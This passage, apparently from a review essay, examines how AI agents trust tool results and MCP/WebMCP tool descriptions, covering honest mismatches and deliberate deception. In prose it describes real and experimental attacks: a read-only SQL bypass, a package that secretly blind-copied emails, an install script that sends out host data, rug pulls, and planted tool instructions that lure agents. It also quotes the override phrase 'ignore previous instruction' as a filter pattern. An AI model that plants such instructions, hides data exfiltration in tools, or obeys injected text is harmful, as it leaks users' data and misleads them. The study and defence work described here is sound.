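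Bronder (2026), in *Does a Tool Result Carry More Authority Than Plain Text?*, ran three studies in August 2026 with Anthropic's Claude Opus 5. The model had to give the color code assigned to an item, or abstain if it lacked a sufficient basis. In the first study, it adopted a false code from a tool result in 14 of 24 trials. When the false code came from an earlier message in the assistant's own voice, it did so in none of the 22 trials that Bronder could score. Adding metadata to the tool result, including a label that marked it as unchecked, did not lower the rate (15 of 24). When the main comparison was repeated four days later, the model adopted the false code in 7 of 24 trials with the tool result and 0 of 24 with the assistant's message.

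The third study suggests that Claude does not give special authority to tools, although the earlier evidence makes it look as if it does. Bronder told the model in advance to inspect two records, one from a tool and one in plain text, and put both in the same message. The model adopted the false code in 57 of 60 trials when it was in the tool result, and in all 60 when it was in the plain text. Bronder concludes that the whole arrangement of the messages matters, and that the tool channel may have no special authority. He also notes that the model had no evidence against the false codes, so adopting them could be a competent way to do the task.

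Shapira, Cheng and Orgad (2026), in *Is Sycophancy a Form of In-Context Updating?*, tested four models, including Claude Opus 5 and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Terra, on multiple-choice questions that the models could answer correctly. They added a claim that a plausible wrong option was right, and varied the claim's source. The models followed credible outside sources far more often than they followed the user's own belief, and a lookup tool that the model itself called was particularly influential. But most models moved nearly as far toward the wrong answer when the user merely reported that the tool had returned it. The influence seems to come mostly from the idea that somebody looked the answer up, which fits Bronder's third study.

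In *Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools*, Yang, Song and colleagues (2026) tested 14 models with three tools: web search, a code executor and a "sub-agent", a second model that summarizes documents. They changed only the relevant answer within each result. The table gives the rates for plausible errors, and its last column includes only items that a model had answered correctly without the tool.

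| Tool | Adopted the false content | Adopted it despite knowing the right answer |
|---|---|---|
| Web search | 68.0% | 56.4% |
| Sub-agent | 40.1% | 26.8% |
| Code executor | 35.5% | 33.5% |

In calculations, six of the models adopted a false number in 40.2 per cent of cases when it came from the code executor, but in only 1.8 per cent when the user supplied the same output. The two set-ups also differed in whether the model had access to tools, so the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the tool's authority. Still, the gap suggests that models don't treat tool results just like any other text.

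When Yang and colleagues replaced the answer with an unrelated one, such as "11" for the name of the German chancellor, the models still adopted it 12.6 per cent of the time. In 88 to 96 per cent of the runs in which two of the Qwen models adopted a false calculation, they had first mentioned a conflict in their reasoning. Across search and calculation, the models warned the user in only 4.2 per cent of the final answers that contained false content.

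Models are much better at noticing a tool that fails openly than one that fails quietly by returning a plausible wrong value. *Loud Failures, Quiet Failures* (Kraishan, 2026) tested six models on multi-step tasks with injected faults. The models treated an explicit error as a problem in 91.3 per cent of trials, and a plausible wrong value in 58.8 per cent. They also reported problems in 26.8 per cent of trials with no injected fault, so the 58.8 per cent includes some false alarms. A tool that overcharges the shopper and returns "success" is a quiet failure in this sense.

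Telling models to be careful has had mixed results. Kraishan told the agent in its prompt to check each result, but this made no difference to detection. Yang and colleagues' instruction to verify conflicting results reduced the adoption of false calculations from 40.2 to 30.4 per cent, but the adoption of false search results only from 75.4 to 70.0 per cent.

More suspicion can also make a model worse at using good information. Shapira and colleagues ran a further test in which half of the suggested answers were correct. Claude Opus 5 followed the user's suggestion 21 per cent of the time, against 78 per cent for Claude Sonnet 5. It also followed sources described as trustworthy only 27 per cent of the time, against 98 per cent for Sonnet 5. An agent like this would reject more false tool results, but it would also ignore many accurate ones.

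The user can't rely on the agent's own account either. In *Fabrication After Tool Failure*, Sethi and Kenzhebayev (2026) gave models tool results that contained no usable answer. In 14.10 per cent of responses, the model either stated a value that the result couldn't support or declined to answer, citing an invented policy or limitation. Requiring the model to first state whether the retrieval had succeeded cut this to 0.87 per cent. This is an easy and effective fix for tools that visibly fail, but if a tool falsely reports success, the model would presumably repeat the false report.

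### Checking through a channel the provider does not control

Checking works much better when the agent can get evidence from a source other than the tool. In *When Tools Silently Lie*, Tao and Yin (2026) gave agents small data tables to analyze and altered the tools' output but not the tables. In one example, the tool returns the correct highest revenue but the wrong store. Such errors lowered the agents' success rate by 26 to 39 percentage points, depending on the software framework.

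Tao and Yin then varied what the agents saw when they looked again. When the data was clean the second time, agents that started over got the right answer in 48 of 48 runs, and agents that reviewed their earlier work got it in 47 of 48. Both groups scored 0 of 48 when the second look was fully corrupted as well. Similarly, Bronder found that Claude Opus 5 adopted none of 96 false codes in a separate run where it could consult an independent checker, though that checker was free and always right, and most agents can't expect to have one like it.

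After calling "finalizeCart", an agent could use another of the shop's tools to check whether an order exists, but the shop controls what both tools return. The shopper's bank keeps its own record of charges, which the shop can't edit, though the best source to check depends on the effect.

| Effect | Independent evidence | What it may miss |
|---|---|---|
| A charge to the user's card | The bank's record | A charge that arrives later |
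| A changed or deleted file on her computer | A comparison with an earlier copy | Changes to files that she didn't copy |
| An upload from her computer | A log of network traffic | What the upload contained, if the tool encrypted it |
| Storage or resale of her data by the provider | Usually none | Nearly everything |

A channel is independent only if the tool can't tamper with it. A program that runs with all of the user's permissions might alter the earlier copy along with the original, which is one reason to run tools in a sandbox. The agent can record the state of an account or folder before a call and compare it afterwards, but by then the effect has occurred, so this is most useful when the user can reverse the effect or when the first call is small. As with Pérez-Acle's rule-breaking programs, one unexpected charge proves that something went wrong, but a statement without one doesn't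 rule out a later charge.

If the weather provider keeps a history of everyone's queries on its own machines, the user won't see it in a bank statement or file listing. Her agent can still control what it sends, and a forecast requires her city but not her street address.

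## Accidental mismatches: stale, vague and overstated descriptions

Honest providers often get their descriptions wrong. The code can show that a description is wrong but seldom why, so the cause of a mismatch in a real tool usually has to be inferred. Shi and colleagues therefore avoid accusing the maintainers of the mismatched tools they found.

### Code changes that the description misses

Suppose a shop offers a tool with the description "Cancel an order free of charge". A year later the shop introduces a $5 cancellation fee, and a programmer adds it to the code. Her automated tests confirm that the code charges $5, but none of them covers the description, so agents keep cancelling orders as if doing so were free.

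Popular servers change often, so their tool descriptions have many chances to become outdated. In *Real Faults in Model Context Protocol (MCP) Software*, Taraghi, Morovati and Khomh (2026) classed 3,282 closed issues from 279 code repositories as bug reports, or about 12 per repository. Some of those reports will have led to no change in the code, but each fix that alters what a tool does can leave its description out of date.

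A tool's description and its code can also have different authors. Shopify, which hosts online shops, puts a standard set of WebMCP tools on its storefronts and writes their descriptions itself. According to Shopify's *WebMCP tools*, a shop's theme (the code that controls how the shop looks) can customize what happens when the cart changes, such as by opening a panel that shows the cart, and an agent's call triggers this behavior too. An extra panel is harmless, but if a theme added paid gift wrapping whenever the cart changed, Shopify's description would become incomplete even though Shopify hadn't changed it.

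Copied code can cause an even larger mismatch. One tool in Shi and colleagues' sample is described as offering real-time weather forecasts by city or district, but its code looks up exchange rates. Weather tools are a stock example in MCP's documentation, so perhaps the programmer copied one, rewrote the code and forgot to update the description. An agent might catch this mistake because the function is called `query_exchange_rates` and takes two currency codes as inputs, but most stale descriptions don't come with such obvious clues.

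### Descriptions written for other programmers

Python programmers often begin a function with a docstring, a short note that explains the function to anyone reading the code. MCP's software kit for Python can use the docstring as the tool's description if the programmer doesn't supply one. In the made-up example below, the first line makes the function available to agents, and the docstring is in triple quotation marks.

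```
@mcp.tool()
def sync_returns(since):
    """Same as sync_orders, but for returns."""
    ...
```

This docstring is fine for a colleague who has the file open, because she can look up `sync_orders` and see that it copies new orders into the accounts and emails each customer. A model that receives only this line has no information that the tool will send hundreds of emails.

If the programmer writes no docstring either, the model gets only a name and an input schema. Shi and colleagues found no explanatory text for 2,170 (11.3 per cent) of the 19,200 tools they extracted. They suggest that some developers don't realize where the software kit gets a tool's description.

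Habits like these may affect a whole server. On servers with more than one mismatched tool, 66 per cent of the mismatched tools had their server's most common type of mismatch. Shi and colleagues suggest that shared templates and documentation styles repeat the same mistake across tools. This is plausible, but the figure is less striking than it looks, because on a server with only two mismatched tools the most common type always accounts for at least half of them.

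### Planned features and reassuring words

Programmers sometimes describe the tool they plan to build and then build only part of it. The most common mismatches in Shi and colleagues' sample were descriptions of features the tool lacked, and they take this as a sign that many descriptions are aspirational. The trading tool that places orders without the confirmation prompt in its description may be an example, if its author meant to add the prompt later.

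Another of their tools has the description "Process some data." Its code takes a number and a name, processes nothing, and returns a sentence stating that it has processed that many items for that name. The tool looks like a placeholder that somebody meant to replace, but an agent that calls it to process 40 invoices will get a message that it has processed 40 items, and may well tell the user that the work is done.

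Providers also overstate what their tools do by adding a reassuring word. One database tool's description is "Execute SQL queries safely on the salaries database." SQL, the usual language for database commands, can change or delete records as well as read them. The tool runs any statement it receives without checking it, then permanently saves any changes. The programmer may have meant by "safely" that the code handles errors or closes its connection properly. An agent is more likely to conclude that the tool can't do any damage, and a badly written command could then overwrite everyone's salary. A far more useful description would be "Runs any SQL statement and permanently saves the changes."

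Sometimes a disputed word in a description is true on one reading. A tool described as "Convert local PDF file to Markdown using OCR" uploads the file to an outside service. (OCR is software that recognizes text in images, and Markdown is a simple text format.) Shi and colleagues interpret the description as a claim that the conversion happens locally. But grammatically "local" describes the file, and the provider may only have meant to distinguish this tool from one that takes a web address. The description still misleads a user who picks the tool to keep a confidential contract on her own computer. Another tool in the sample avoids the problem by naming the company that receives the file, with the words "Sends document to Unstructured".

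### What "finalizeCart" could mean

The name "finalizeCart" is ambiguous in the same way, but misreading it costs money. Huang gives two readings, that the tool displays the cart or that it makes a purchase. A third reading falls between them, that the tool locks the cart's contents, adds tax and delivery, and takes the shopper to the checkout without buying anything.

Suppose the shopper has asked to see her cart. Her request doesn't show what the tool does, but an agent could easily decide that "finalizeCart" must display the cart because it needs a tool that does. Other clues are more relevant, though none is reliable.

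| Clue | Suggests a display | Suggests a purchase | Why it might mislead |
|---|---|---|---|
| Other tools on the page | There is a separate "placeOrder" tool | There is a separate "viewCart" tool | The shop may have two tools for the same job |
| The tool's inputs | It takes none | It takes a card number or delivery address | A shop that has her card on file needs no inputs to charge it |
| The current page | She is browsing products | She has filled in the checkout form | The shop may offer the same tools on every page |

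The provider could also attach a read-only label, which would settle the question if the label were accurate.

If the available clues don't settle what the tool does, the agent should compare the cost of a mistake with the cost of asking. Suppose undoing an unwanted purchase would cost the shopper $10 in time and postage, and answering a question would cost her 10 cents' worth of attention. If p is the probability that the tool makes a purchase, calling it without asking is worthwhile only if p × $10 is less than $0.10, so p has to be below 1 per cent. It's hard to see how an agent could be that confident from this name. But it may not need to ask, because it could open the cart page and read the contents there.

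Translation makes the name riskier. Spanish-language shops commonly label the checkout button "Finalizar compra", so a Spanish-speaking programmer choosing an English name might write "finalizeCart" and assume it means buying. An agent that learned mainly from English text may be more likely to think it displays the cart. A shop might also intend the tool only as a final review, while a Spanish-speaking shopper's agent associates the word with the checkout button and thinks the tool places the order. A shop could test for this by asking several agents to show the cart, in each language it serves, and counting how many call the tool.

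A better name would prevent most of these mistakes. Chrome for Developers (2026) advises providers to distinguish, in a tool's name, between carrying out an action and starting a process that leads to it. In its example, `create-event` creates a calendar event immediately, while `start-event-creation-process` takes the user to a form.

Shopify separates the steps of a purchase into different tools. On its storefronts, `get_cart` returns the cart's contents and `proceed_to_checkout` takes the shopper to the checkout. The checkout registers the tools for placing an order only when the shopper arrives, so an agent can't call one by mistake while the shopper is still browsing. If a request to `update_cart` is unclear, the tool returns a list of options instead of changing the cart.

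A shop with a "finalizeCart" tool could replace it with two tools. The explanatory text might read as follows.

```
show_cart
  "Show the items, quantities and total price in the
   shopper's cart. Does not change the cart or place
   an order."

place_order
  "Buy everything in the cart now. Charges the shopper's
   saved card and emails a receipt."
  input: expected_total, the amount the shopper agreed to pay
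```

`place_order` takes the agreed amount as input. This makes the tool's purpose hard to miss, because an agent that is only checking the cart has no such amount to enter. The shop's code can also use this amount to reject the order if the total has changed since the shopper saw it.

If a cart tool doesn't place orders, it is worth including "Does not place an order" in its description, because people expect some cart tools to do so. Chrome for Developers recommends positive wording and would leave a tool's limits implicit, but its example of what to avoid is "Don't use this tool for weather" in the description of a calendar tool. The advice is sensible in that case because nobody would expect a calendar tool to forecast the weather.

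### Conveniences that the provider leaves out

A programmer may add a feature for convenience and not think of it as part of what the tool does. Shi and colleagues found a tool with the description "Save the generated server code to a file." After saving the file, the tool also changes its permissions so that every account on the computer can read and run it. The provider probably did this because people who generate a server usually want to run it. On a shared machine, though, the tool gives everyone access to a file that the user only asked it to save.

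The tool that sends documents to Unstructured has a similar fault. Its description clearly discloses the upload and covers returning the text, but leaves out that the code also saves a file of intermediate results on each call. One file hardly matters, but an agent processing a company's archive would leave thousands. These take up disk space and contain text from documents that the company may later try to delete.

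Logging is probably the easiest of these features to forget to mention, since programmers may add it years after somebody wrote the description. Shi and colleagues give the illustration of a weather provider that keeps a history of queries. Such a provider could honestly think of this as housekeeping, even though the cities someone asks about can reveal where she is travelling.

Leftover test code can make a tool leak secrets that its description doesn't mention. One tool, described as "Echo a message as a tool", returns the user's message along with a secret key from the server's settings. A programmer may have printed the key to check that the settings had loaded, then published the tool without removing that line. Shi and colleagues point out that an attacker could hide a leak behind an equally ordinary description.

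### Safeguards that fail

Some providers describe a safeguard that they did build but that doesn't work. A well-known example is Anthropic's reference MCP server for Postgres, a widely used database. The server offered a tool for running a "read-only SQL query". In 2025 Datadog Security Labs reported that the tool could be made to write to the database.

The server relied on a transaction, which is a group of commands that the database handles as a unit. For each call, it took three steps:

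1. It opened a read-only transaction, in which the database refuses commands that change records.
2. It ran the text that the agent had sent.
3. It rolled the transaction back, which would undo anything done inside it.

The weakness was in the second step. The server's database library accepted several commands in one piece of text, and one of them could close the transaction. Any later command in the same text then ran outside the read-only restriction, and the rollback at the end could not undo it.

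Ordinary testing could easily have missed this. A developer who sent the tool a single command to delete a record would have seen the database refuse it and could reasonably have concluded that the safeguard worked. The description was accurate for nearly every query an honest agent would send. But read-only access matters most when an agent is confused or someone has tricked it, and a user who trusted the description might have connected the tool to an account with full permission to change her data.

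A provider can close this gap by sending the text as a prepared statement, which PostgreSQL limits to one command. Giving the tool a database account without write permission is safer still, because that safeguard doesn't depend on how the server handles the text.

Repairs can also lead to accidental mismatches. *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (Shi, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool on the Markdownify server that converts web pages to Markdown. An attacker could trick an agent into using it to fetch private pages from the server's own machine. A contributor added a filter to block private addresses, but a user later commented that the check was minimal and that anyone could bypass it with the same methods that worked on the project it came from. If the provider had updated the description to state that the tool refuses private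 addresses, the provider would have sincerely made a false claim.

### How good descriptions are in practice

Shi, Fu and colleagues at Tongji University in China also studied how much providers put in their descriptions. They searched GitHub for MCP servers, ranked the results by popularity, and screened them by hand to select 100. They then connected to each server and collected what a model would see for each tool, covering 1,856 tools in total. For 65 per cent of the tools, the description gave only the basic function, in little more than one sentence on average. Another 28 per cent included practical constraints such as input requirements, and 7 per cent included security restrictions or warnings about misuse.

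The descriptions of inputs were more detailed, averaging about 100 tokens (words or parts of words) per tool, compared with 55 for the main text, and 77 per cent included constraints. Providers seem to take more care to explain how to call a tool than what the call will do. That makes sense for a programmer trying to prevent failed calls, since a badly formed input causes an error that somebody notices, while an undisclosed upload causes no such error.

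A short description can still be true, so these figures don't measure mismatches. *From Docs to Descriptions* compares descriptions with code in a much larger sample of 10,831 servers from GitHub and four other public collections. The researchers extracted each tool's description and code, and had GPT-4o mini, a small OpenAI model, list the problems in each pair. The model grouped the problems as it went, and the researchers then matched the groups to existing standards for software documentation. This produced 18 types of problem, which they call "smells". The table gives seven of them, with invented examples.

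| Problem | Cases | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Repeated tool name | 7,894 | Several servers each offer a tool called `read_file` |
| Wrong meaning of an input | 3,449 | The text asks for an amount in dollars, but the code treats it as cents |
| No description of the result | 3,093 | A price look-up doesn't specify the currency |
| Undeclared behavior | 931 | A file search also searches the user's email |
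| Missing side effects | 773 | A report tool also emails the report to a manager |
| Claimed behavior that doesn't exist | 572 | A translation tool offers Welsh, but the code has no Welsh option |
| Behavior that contradicts the text | 72 | A tool for archiving messages deletes them |

The most common problem is that servers share tool names, which isn't a mismatch because a name like `read_file` may be accurate on every server that uses it. Descriptions that misstate what an input means are more worrying. If a description says an amount is in dollars but the tool reads it as cents, an agent that enters 50 for a $50 refund would send the customer 50 cents, even though the tool's name and stated purpose are correct.

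These counts are approximate, because they depend on a small model's judgment and the paper sometimes treats them as numbers of servers and sometimes as numbers of tools. The researchers examined each server at one point in time, so they couldn't tell which descriptions had been true when they were written. They call the general pattern "code-first, description-last". That fits the data, but they would need to follow the same tools over time to show how many descriptions go stale.

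### What better descriptions change

*From Docs to Descriptions* also reports two experiments on how descriptions affect a model's choice of tool, again with GPT-4o mini. In the first, for each of ten types of server, the researchers wrote several descriptions of the same code, each strong or weak on one quality. They replaced the tools' names with random identifiers so that names couldn't influence the choice. They then gave the model 1,000 requests, which ranged from "Read file" to a detailed account of a fault that included the file's full path.

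| Quality of the description | Chosen when strong | Chosen when weak | Difference in percentage points |
|---|---|---|---|
| Clear about function and when to use the tool | 17.8% | 6.2% | 11.6 |
| Accurate about behavior and inputs | 15.9% | 7.1% | 8.8 |
| Complete | 14.3% | 8.4% | 5.9 |
| Concise | 10.6% | 9.1% | 1.5 |

A clear statement of function mattered most for very short requests, where the difference rose to 14.2 points. Completeness mattered more when the request was detailed.

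The model never saw the code, so the result for accuracy must come from something in the wording, such as precise details about inputs. A false description with equally precise details would probably have worked just as well.

In the second experiment, the researchers assembled ten groups of five real servers that did the same job, such as managing calendars, and rewrote one server's description in each group to meet their standard. The model chose the server with the rewritten description 72 per cent of the time on average, and between 65 and 81 per cent in individual groups. The researchers compare this with the 20 per cent expected by chance, not with how often the model chose the same server before the rewrite, so the effect of rewriting could be smaller or larger than the comparison suggests.

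This gives providers a commercial reason to write better descriptions, but it doesn't show that users get better results. All five servers in a group did the same job, and the experiment measured which one the model chose, not whether it completed the task. A provider could also get more calls by describing features that don't exist. An honest provider may do this unintentionally if she keeps whichever wording attracts the most use and never checks it against the code.

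Better descriptions can also make agents use a tool more carefully. Shi, Fu and colleagues added security guidance to the descriptions of vulnerable tools and had the model review its planned calls. With both measures in place, malicious requests succeeded only 0.13 per cent of the time in a test based on 792 prompts. However, neither measure fixes the vulnerable code, so the protection lasts only as long as the agent follows the guidance.

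### When a web accelerator deleted users' data

The web had a similar problem long before AI agents. Each request a browser sends to a website has a method, which labels the kind of request. Ordinary links use GET, which is for fetching a page, while forms that change something normally use POST. The current standard, *HTTP Semantics* (RFC 9110; Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), classes GET as "safe", meaning that its defined purpose is essentially read-only. The 1999 version already had this convention.

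Many sites nevertheless used ordinary links for actions such as deleting a page. This caused little trouble while people clicked the links themselves, because they could see the word "Delete" and often had to confirm in a pop-up box. In May 2005 Google released Web Accelerator, a program that sped up browsing by fetching the pages behind links before the user clicked. It treated GET links as safe to follow, including the ones that deleted things.

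The software company 37signals warned about the accelerator on its blog that month, after users of its Backpack organizer lost data. The company explained that the accelerator was in effect clicking every link on the page, and that pop-up confirmations didn't stop it, because it requested each linked address directly.

The developers of these sites weren't trying to deceive anyone, and many probably never thought of a link as a claim about what it did. They made that claim just by using a link, much as a Python programmer can publish a tool description by writing a docstring. The mismatch could go unnoticed for years because human visitors relied on the visible text, but it became harmful when a program relied on the HTTP method instead.

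*HTTP Semantics* allows a safe request to have some effects. For example, a server may log each visit, because the visitor didn't ask for the log and so isn't accountable for it. But if an address performs an unsafe action such as deleting a page, the site's owner must disable that action for GET requests. The standard warns that automated programs will otherwise trigger such actions when they follow every link to fetch pages in advance or build a search index.

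## Deliberate deception by tool providers

A dishonest provider can choose which part of a tool's description to make false, whereas honest mistakes can fall anywhere in it. The dishonest provider will usually keep the rest of the description accurate, because users soon abandon a tool that fails at its advertised job.

### What a provider can gain

The most obvious gain is more business. Suppose five equally good translation tools each charge one cent per call. If agents choose among them at random, each tool gets 2,000 of every 10,000 requests and earns $20. *From Docs to Descriptions* found that the model chose the server with a rewritten description 72 per cent of the time. A translation tool with that share would earn $72. A provider who invented features might earn just as much.

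A provider may also want the user's data, and can hide the collection in a tool that needs that data for a routine job. An email tool has to receive a message to send it, so the provider can keep a copy without asking for anything unusual. The email still arrives, so the user has no reason to look further.

A provider can lie about what data a job requires. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, tested this with four host applications and three models. Their malicious tool failed on purpose and returned a false error message saying that a required input was missing. The message was designed to work much like an instruction, so that the model would fetch private information, or misuse another tool, and try again. On a simple average across their tests, this worked 88 per cent of the time, compared with 75 per cent for instructions planted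 in the tool's description. They ran each test only five times, and the newest model dates from 2025.

A provider can easily claim a safeguard that its tool lacks. The claim doesn't benefit the provider directly, but it may lead the host or the user to drop a check that would have exposed another lie.

Finally, a provider can behave honestly until people trust the tool. This delays any gain from the deception, but it needn't take much work, since the provider can copy someone else's good tool. An attacker may even be able to take over trust that another provider earned. Li and Gao found 212 registry listings whose owners had deleted their GitHub accounts, leaving the account names free to register. Another 304 listings used the old names of renamed accounts, which were also free. Anyone who registered one of these names could publish a new server at an address that users already trusted.

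### Tools that claim to be better than their rivals

In *MCPXKIT*, Guo, Liu and colleagues (2025) tested how easily a malicious tool can displace a benign one. They ran each attack ten times and counted a run as a success if the agent used the malicious tool or produced the result the attacker wanted. The table's columns are the four benign tools.

| What the malicious tool's description does | Weather | Fetch | Search servers | Use tool |
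|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claims the benign tool is out of date and directs the model to the malicious one | 100% | 80% | 90% | 80% |
| Claims to be the best tool | 70% | 90% | 80% | 50% |
| Changes how the model uses the benign tool ("shadowing") | 80% | 70% | Not reported | Not reported |

Guo and colleagues are probably right to conclude that agents depend heavily on descriptions, but these figures are hard to interpret without knowing how often the agent would have picked the malicious tool anyway. The closest thing to a baseline is another of their tests, in which the two tools had similar descriptions and the agent chose the malicious one half the time, as expected by chance. If that is a fair comparison, claiming to be the best raised the rate from 50 per cent to about 73 per cent (29 of 40 runs), though it made no difference for the fourth tool. Claiming that the rival was out of date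 worked in 35 of 40 runs, but a gap of six runs could be due to chance. Guo and colleagues also don't name the model they tested, so we can't tell whether a current one would do better.

The three attacks involve different amounts of lying. Calling a rival tool "out of date" is a specific claim that is false if the rival still works, although this attack also directs the model to a particular tool. Calling a tool "best" is so vague that it is hardly a claim. Shadowing relies on planted instructions.

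Guo and colleagues also tested tools advertised as having a function they lack. In their example, a tool is supposed to provide real-time stock prices but has no source for them, so the agent gives the user an invented figure. This attack succeeded in 70 per cent of runs.

A provider can refine the wording of a tool's description by trial and error. Guo and colleagues cite earlier work by Wang and colleagues, who used a genetic algorithm to improve their descriptions. Such an algorithm makes many small changes to a text, keeps the versions that work best, and repeats the process. This requires only a record of which wording the model picks, whether or not that wording is true.

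### Luring an agent to a tool it does not need

In the tests with rival tools, the malicious tool offered to do something the user wanted. It is harder for an attacker to get an agent to call a tool that the user's request doesn't require. Lee, Chang and colleagues studied this in *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (June 2026). They assumed that a web page loads a script from a third party, such as an advertiser, and that the script registers an extra WebMCP tool on the page. The tool's provider is then unknown to both the shopper and the shop.

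The agents ran on GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 2.5 Flash. Each had to complete four tasks: saving an article to a knowledge base, emailing a sales report, checking out of a shop, and updating a graphics driver. An attack succeeded if the agent called the malicious tool, which immediately sent data from the task to the attacker. The table gives the success rates across the four tasks for seven of the ten attacks.

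| What the attacker supplied | GPT-5.4 | Claude Opus 4.6 | Gemini 2.5 Flash | Average |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| A neutral name and description | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| A read-only label and matching text | 10% | 8% | 0% | 6% |
| A claim that a legitimate tool needs this one's output | 8% | 30% | 0% | 13% |
| A claim that company policy requires the tool | 18% | 0% | 32% | 17% |
| A plausible business name | 55% | 50% | 12% | 39% |
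| An order to call the tool, within 1,203 words of text | 35% | 0% | 72% | 36% |
| A short order to call the tool before a legitimate step | 78% | 38% | 62% | 59% |

The second, third and fourth rows are mainly false claims, and the last two are planted instructions. The false claims worked much less often. This isn't surprising, since a false claim only gives the model a reason to consider the tool, whereas an instruction tells it what to do. The claim about company policy is borderline because it is a false statement that works as an instruction.

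The row for business names is harder to classify. Lee and colleagues attribute the 39 per cent to the name alone, but elsewhere they say the same condition included a warning that reports may display incorrectly if the agent skips the tool. If the warning was present, its false claim may account for part of the 39 per cent. They also label the attack in the third row "title based", although their example puts the claim in the description.

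The long description padded its order with text about security and data protection standards, in an attempt to avoid scrutiny by sounding compliant. The padding had opposite effects on different models. Gemini followed the padded order more often than the short one, while Claude never called the tool in 40 runs. Lee and colleagues suggest that Claude may have taken the padding as a warning sign.

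The read-only label, which MCP and WebMCP call `readOnlyHint`, worked only 6 per cent of the time in the main experiment. In a follow-up that used a single task, the label alone worked in 87 per cent of runs on average, which Lee and colleagues take as evidence that it can influence a model by itself. But the tool's name also changed, from `diagnostic_probe` in the neutral baseline to `audit_logger` in the labelled version, so the result may not be due to the label alone.

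Another condition in the follow-up, in which the tool was also called `audit_logger` but had altered input descriptions and no read-only label, helps to separate the effect of the label from that of the name. GPT-5.4 and Claude never called this tool, but they called the labelled one in 60 and 100 per cent of runs respectively, so the label probably affected them. Gemini called the tool every time in both conditions, which the name could explain. All the rates in the follow-up are multiples of 20 per cent, which is consistent with only five runs each. The effect of a false read-only label seems to range from very small to large, depending on the setting.

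A user would probably miss most of these attacks, because the agents still completed the original task in 81 per cent of runs with the short order and 85 per cent with the long one. But Lee and colleagues didn't test whether users notice, and they ran the experiments on software that imitates WebMCP, so Chrome's own version might behave differently.

### The postmark-mcp package

A deceptive provider doesn't need to lure users if its tool does what they want. In September 2025, the security company Koi reported such a case, which it called the first malicious MCP server found in real use.

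Postmark is a service that companies use to send emails such as receipts and password resets. It publishes an MCP server on GitHub that lets agents send emails through the service. A developer with no connection to Postmark copied this server and published it as `postmark-mcp` on npm, the main public registry for JavaScript packages. According to Koi, the first 15 versions worked as they should. Version 1.0.16 added one line of code that sent a blind copy of every email to an address that appears to be the developer's. The agent still got its usual success message, and recipients can't see who gets a blind copy.

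Postmark's statement supports the main points. It describes a fake package that built trust over 15 versions and then added a back door in version 1.0.16. Postmark had no involvement in the package and had not published its own server on npm before the incident. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), an entry in a public database of malicious packages, also lists version 1.0.16. The entry is dated 26 September, a day after Koi's report according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails*, so it may not be fully independent of that report.

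Koi's account of how far people trusted the package is less convincing. According to The Hacker News (2025), the developer uploaded the package on 15 September and released version 1.0.16 on 17 September, so it was legitimate for about two days. Koi, however, describes it as having become part of developers' daily work, and warns that a tool can be legitimate for months before it turns malicious.

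The number of victims is also uncertain. Koi started from 1,500 downloads a week, assumed that about 20 per cent were in active use, and treated each of those as a separate organization sending 10 to 50 emails a day. This gives 300 organizations and 3,000 to 15,000 copied emails a day. Only the downloads were counted, and The Hacker News reports a total of 1,643. One organization may download a package many times, and automated services that copy or scan new packages add to the total. Koi, which sells a product that blocks such packages, calls its figures a guess.

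The developer's motive is unknown. He did not reply when Koi asked him for an explanation, and he then deleted the package from npm. He could conceivably have added the blind copy while testing and forgotten to remove it. The use of Postmark's name and the unexplained deletion make that less likely, and both Postmark and the database entry treat the package as malicious. Deleting the package from npm did not remove copies that people had already installed, which could go on sending out their emails.

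This is misrepresentation by omission, since the tool did send email, as its description said. The provider didn't need any of the wording tricks from the experiments, because people who wanted to use Postmark searched for a package with that name.

Some packages collect data during installation, before an agent has read any tool description, so choosing carefully among the tools can't prevent it. OSV's July entry *MAL-2026-6922* (2026) describes an npm package, `mcp-server-pg`, whose install script collects details such as the computer's name, the user's name and the email addresses of people who worked on the project, and sends them to a fixed address.

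### Why registry surveys find so few

Li and Gao's survey found little evidence of this kind of fraud. In June and July 2025 they collected 67,057 servers from six public registries. They checked the tool descriptions from four of the registries and found only 18 servers with suspicious ones. Most of the 18 were demonstrations, including a deliberately vulnerable server for teaching security. In five cases the description only contained an instruction for the model to call another tool, and the provider seems not to have realized that the host might call the wrong one.

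However, the survey was designed to find planted instructions. Its filter searched for variations on "ignore previous instruction" and for labels meant to draw the model's attention, such as "important". It would miss a false claim in ordinary wording, or a true description that omits a data transfer. The description of an email tool like `postmark-mcp` would not need to contain any of the phrases the filter searched for.

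Shi and colleagues found that about a tenth of tools have inconsistent descriptions, but they couldn't tell how many of the mismatches were deliberate, so their survey doesn't show how common deception is either. The two surveys are compatible. In mid-2025, crude planted instructions seem to have been rare in public registries, while mismatches were common.

### Changes after approval

A provider can change a tool's description after a user has approved it. In a notice on 1 April 2025, Invariant Labs named this the "rug pull", after the financial slang for a scam in which promoters attract investors and then disappear with their money. The two experiments in that notice used descriptions that were malicious from the start, but Invariant Labs demonstrated a rug pull in a separate attack on WhatsApp.

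1. The user connects her agent to a genuine WhatsApp server and to the attacker's server, which offers a "random fact of the day".
2. She approves the harmless tool.
3. The next time the host loads the attacker's server, it receives a different tool, whose description contains instructions about how to use WhatsApp.
4. The agent follows these instructions and leaks her message history.

The code is in Invariant Labs' *mcp-injection-experiments*. The harm in this case came from planted instructions, but a provider could exploit the same weakness to misrepresent a tool without planting any. For example, a shopper could approve a dress-search tool that asks only for size and price, and the shop could later add "pregnancy status" to its inputs.

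Hosts make such changes easy. Li and Gao found that the hosts they tested fetch a server's latest descriptions when the user restarts the application, changes its settings, or switches the server off and on. None of the hosts checked the new text. A server's code can change in the same way. Many users start local servers with the command `npx`, which downloads the newest version each time if they add the tag `latest`. A user who set up `postmark-mcp` like this on Monday 15 September could by Wednesday have been running the version that copied her emails.

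On 9 April, the software developer and blogger Simon Willison responded to the warning by calling tools that redefine themselves "a huge issue". He attributed the underlying problem to the models, which trust any text that sounds convincing enough (Willison, 2025). If he is right, a host that alerts users to changed descriptions will help, but it will not protect them from descriptions that are malicious from the start.

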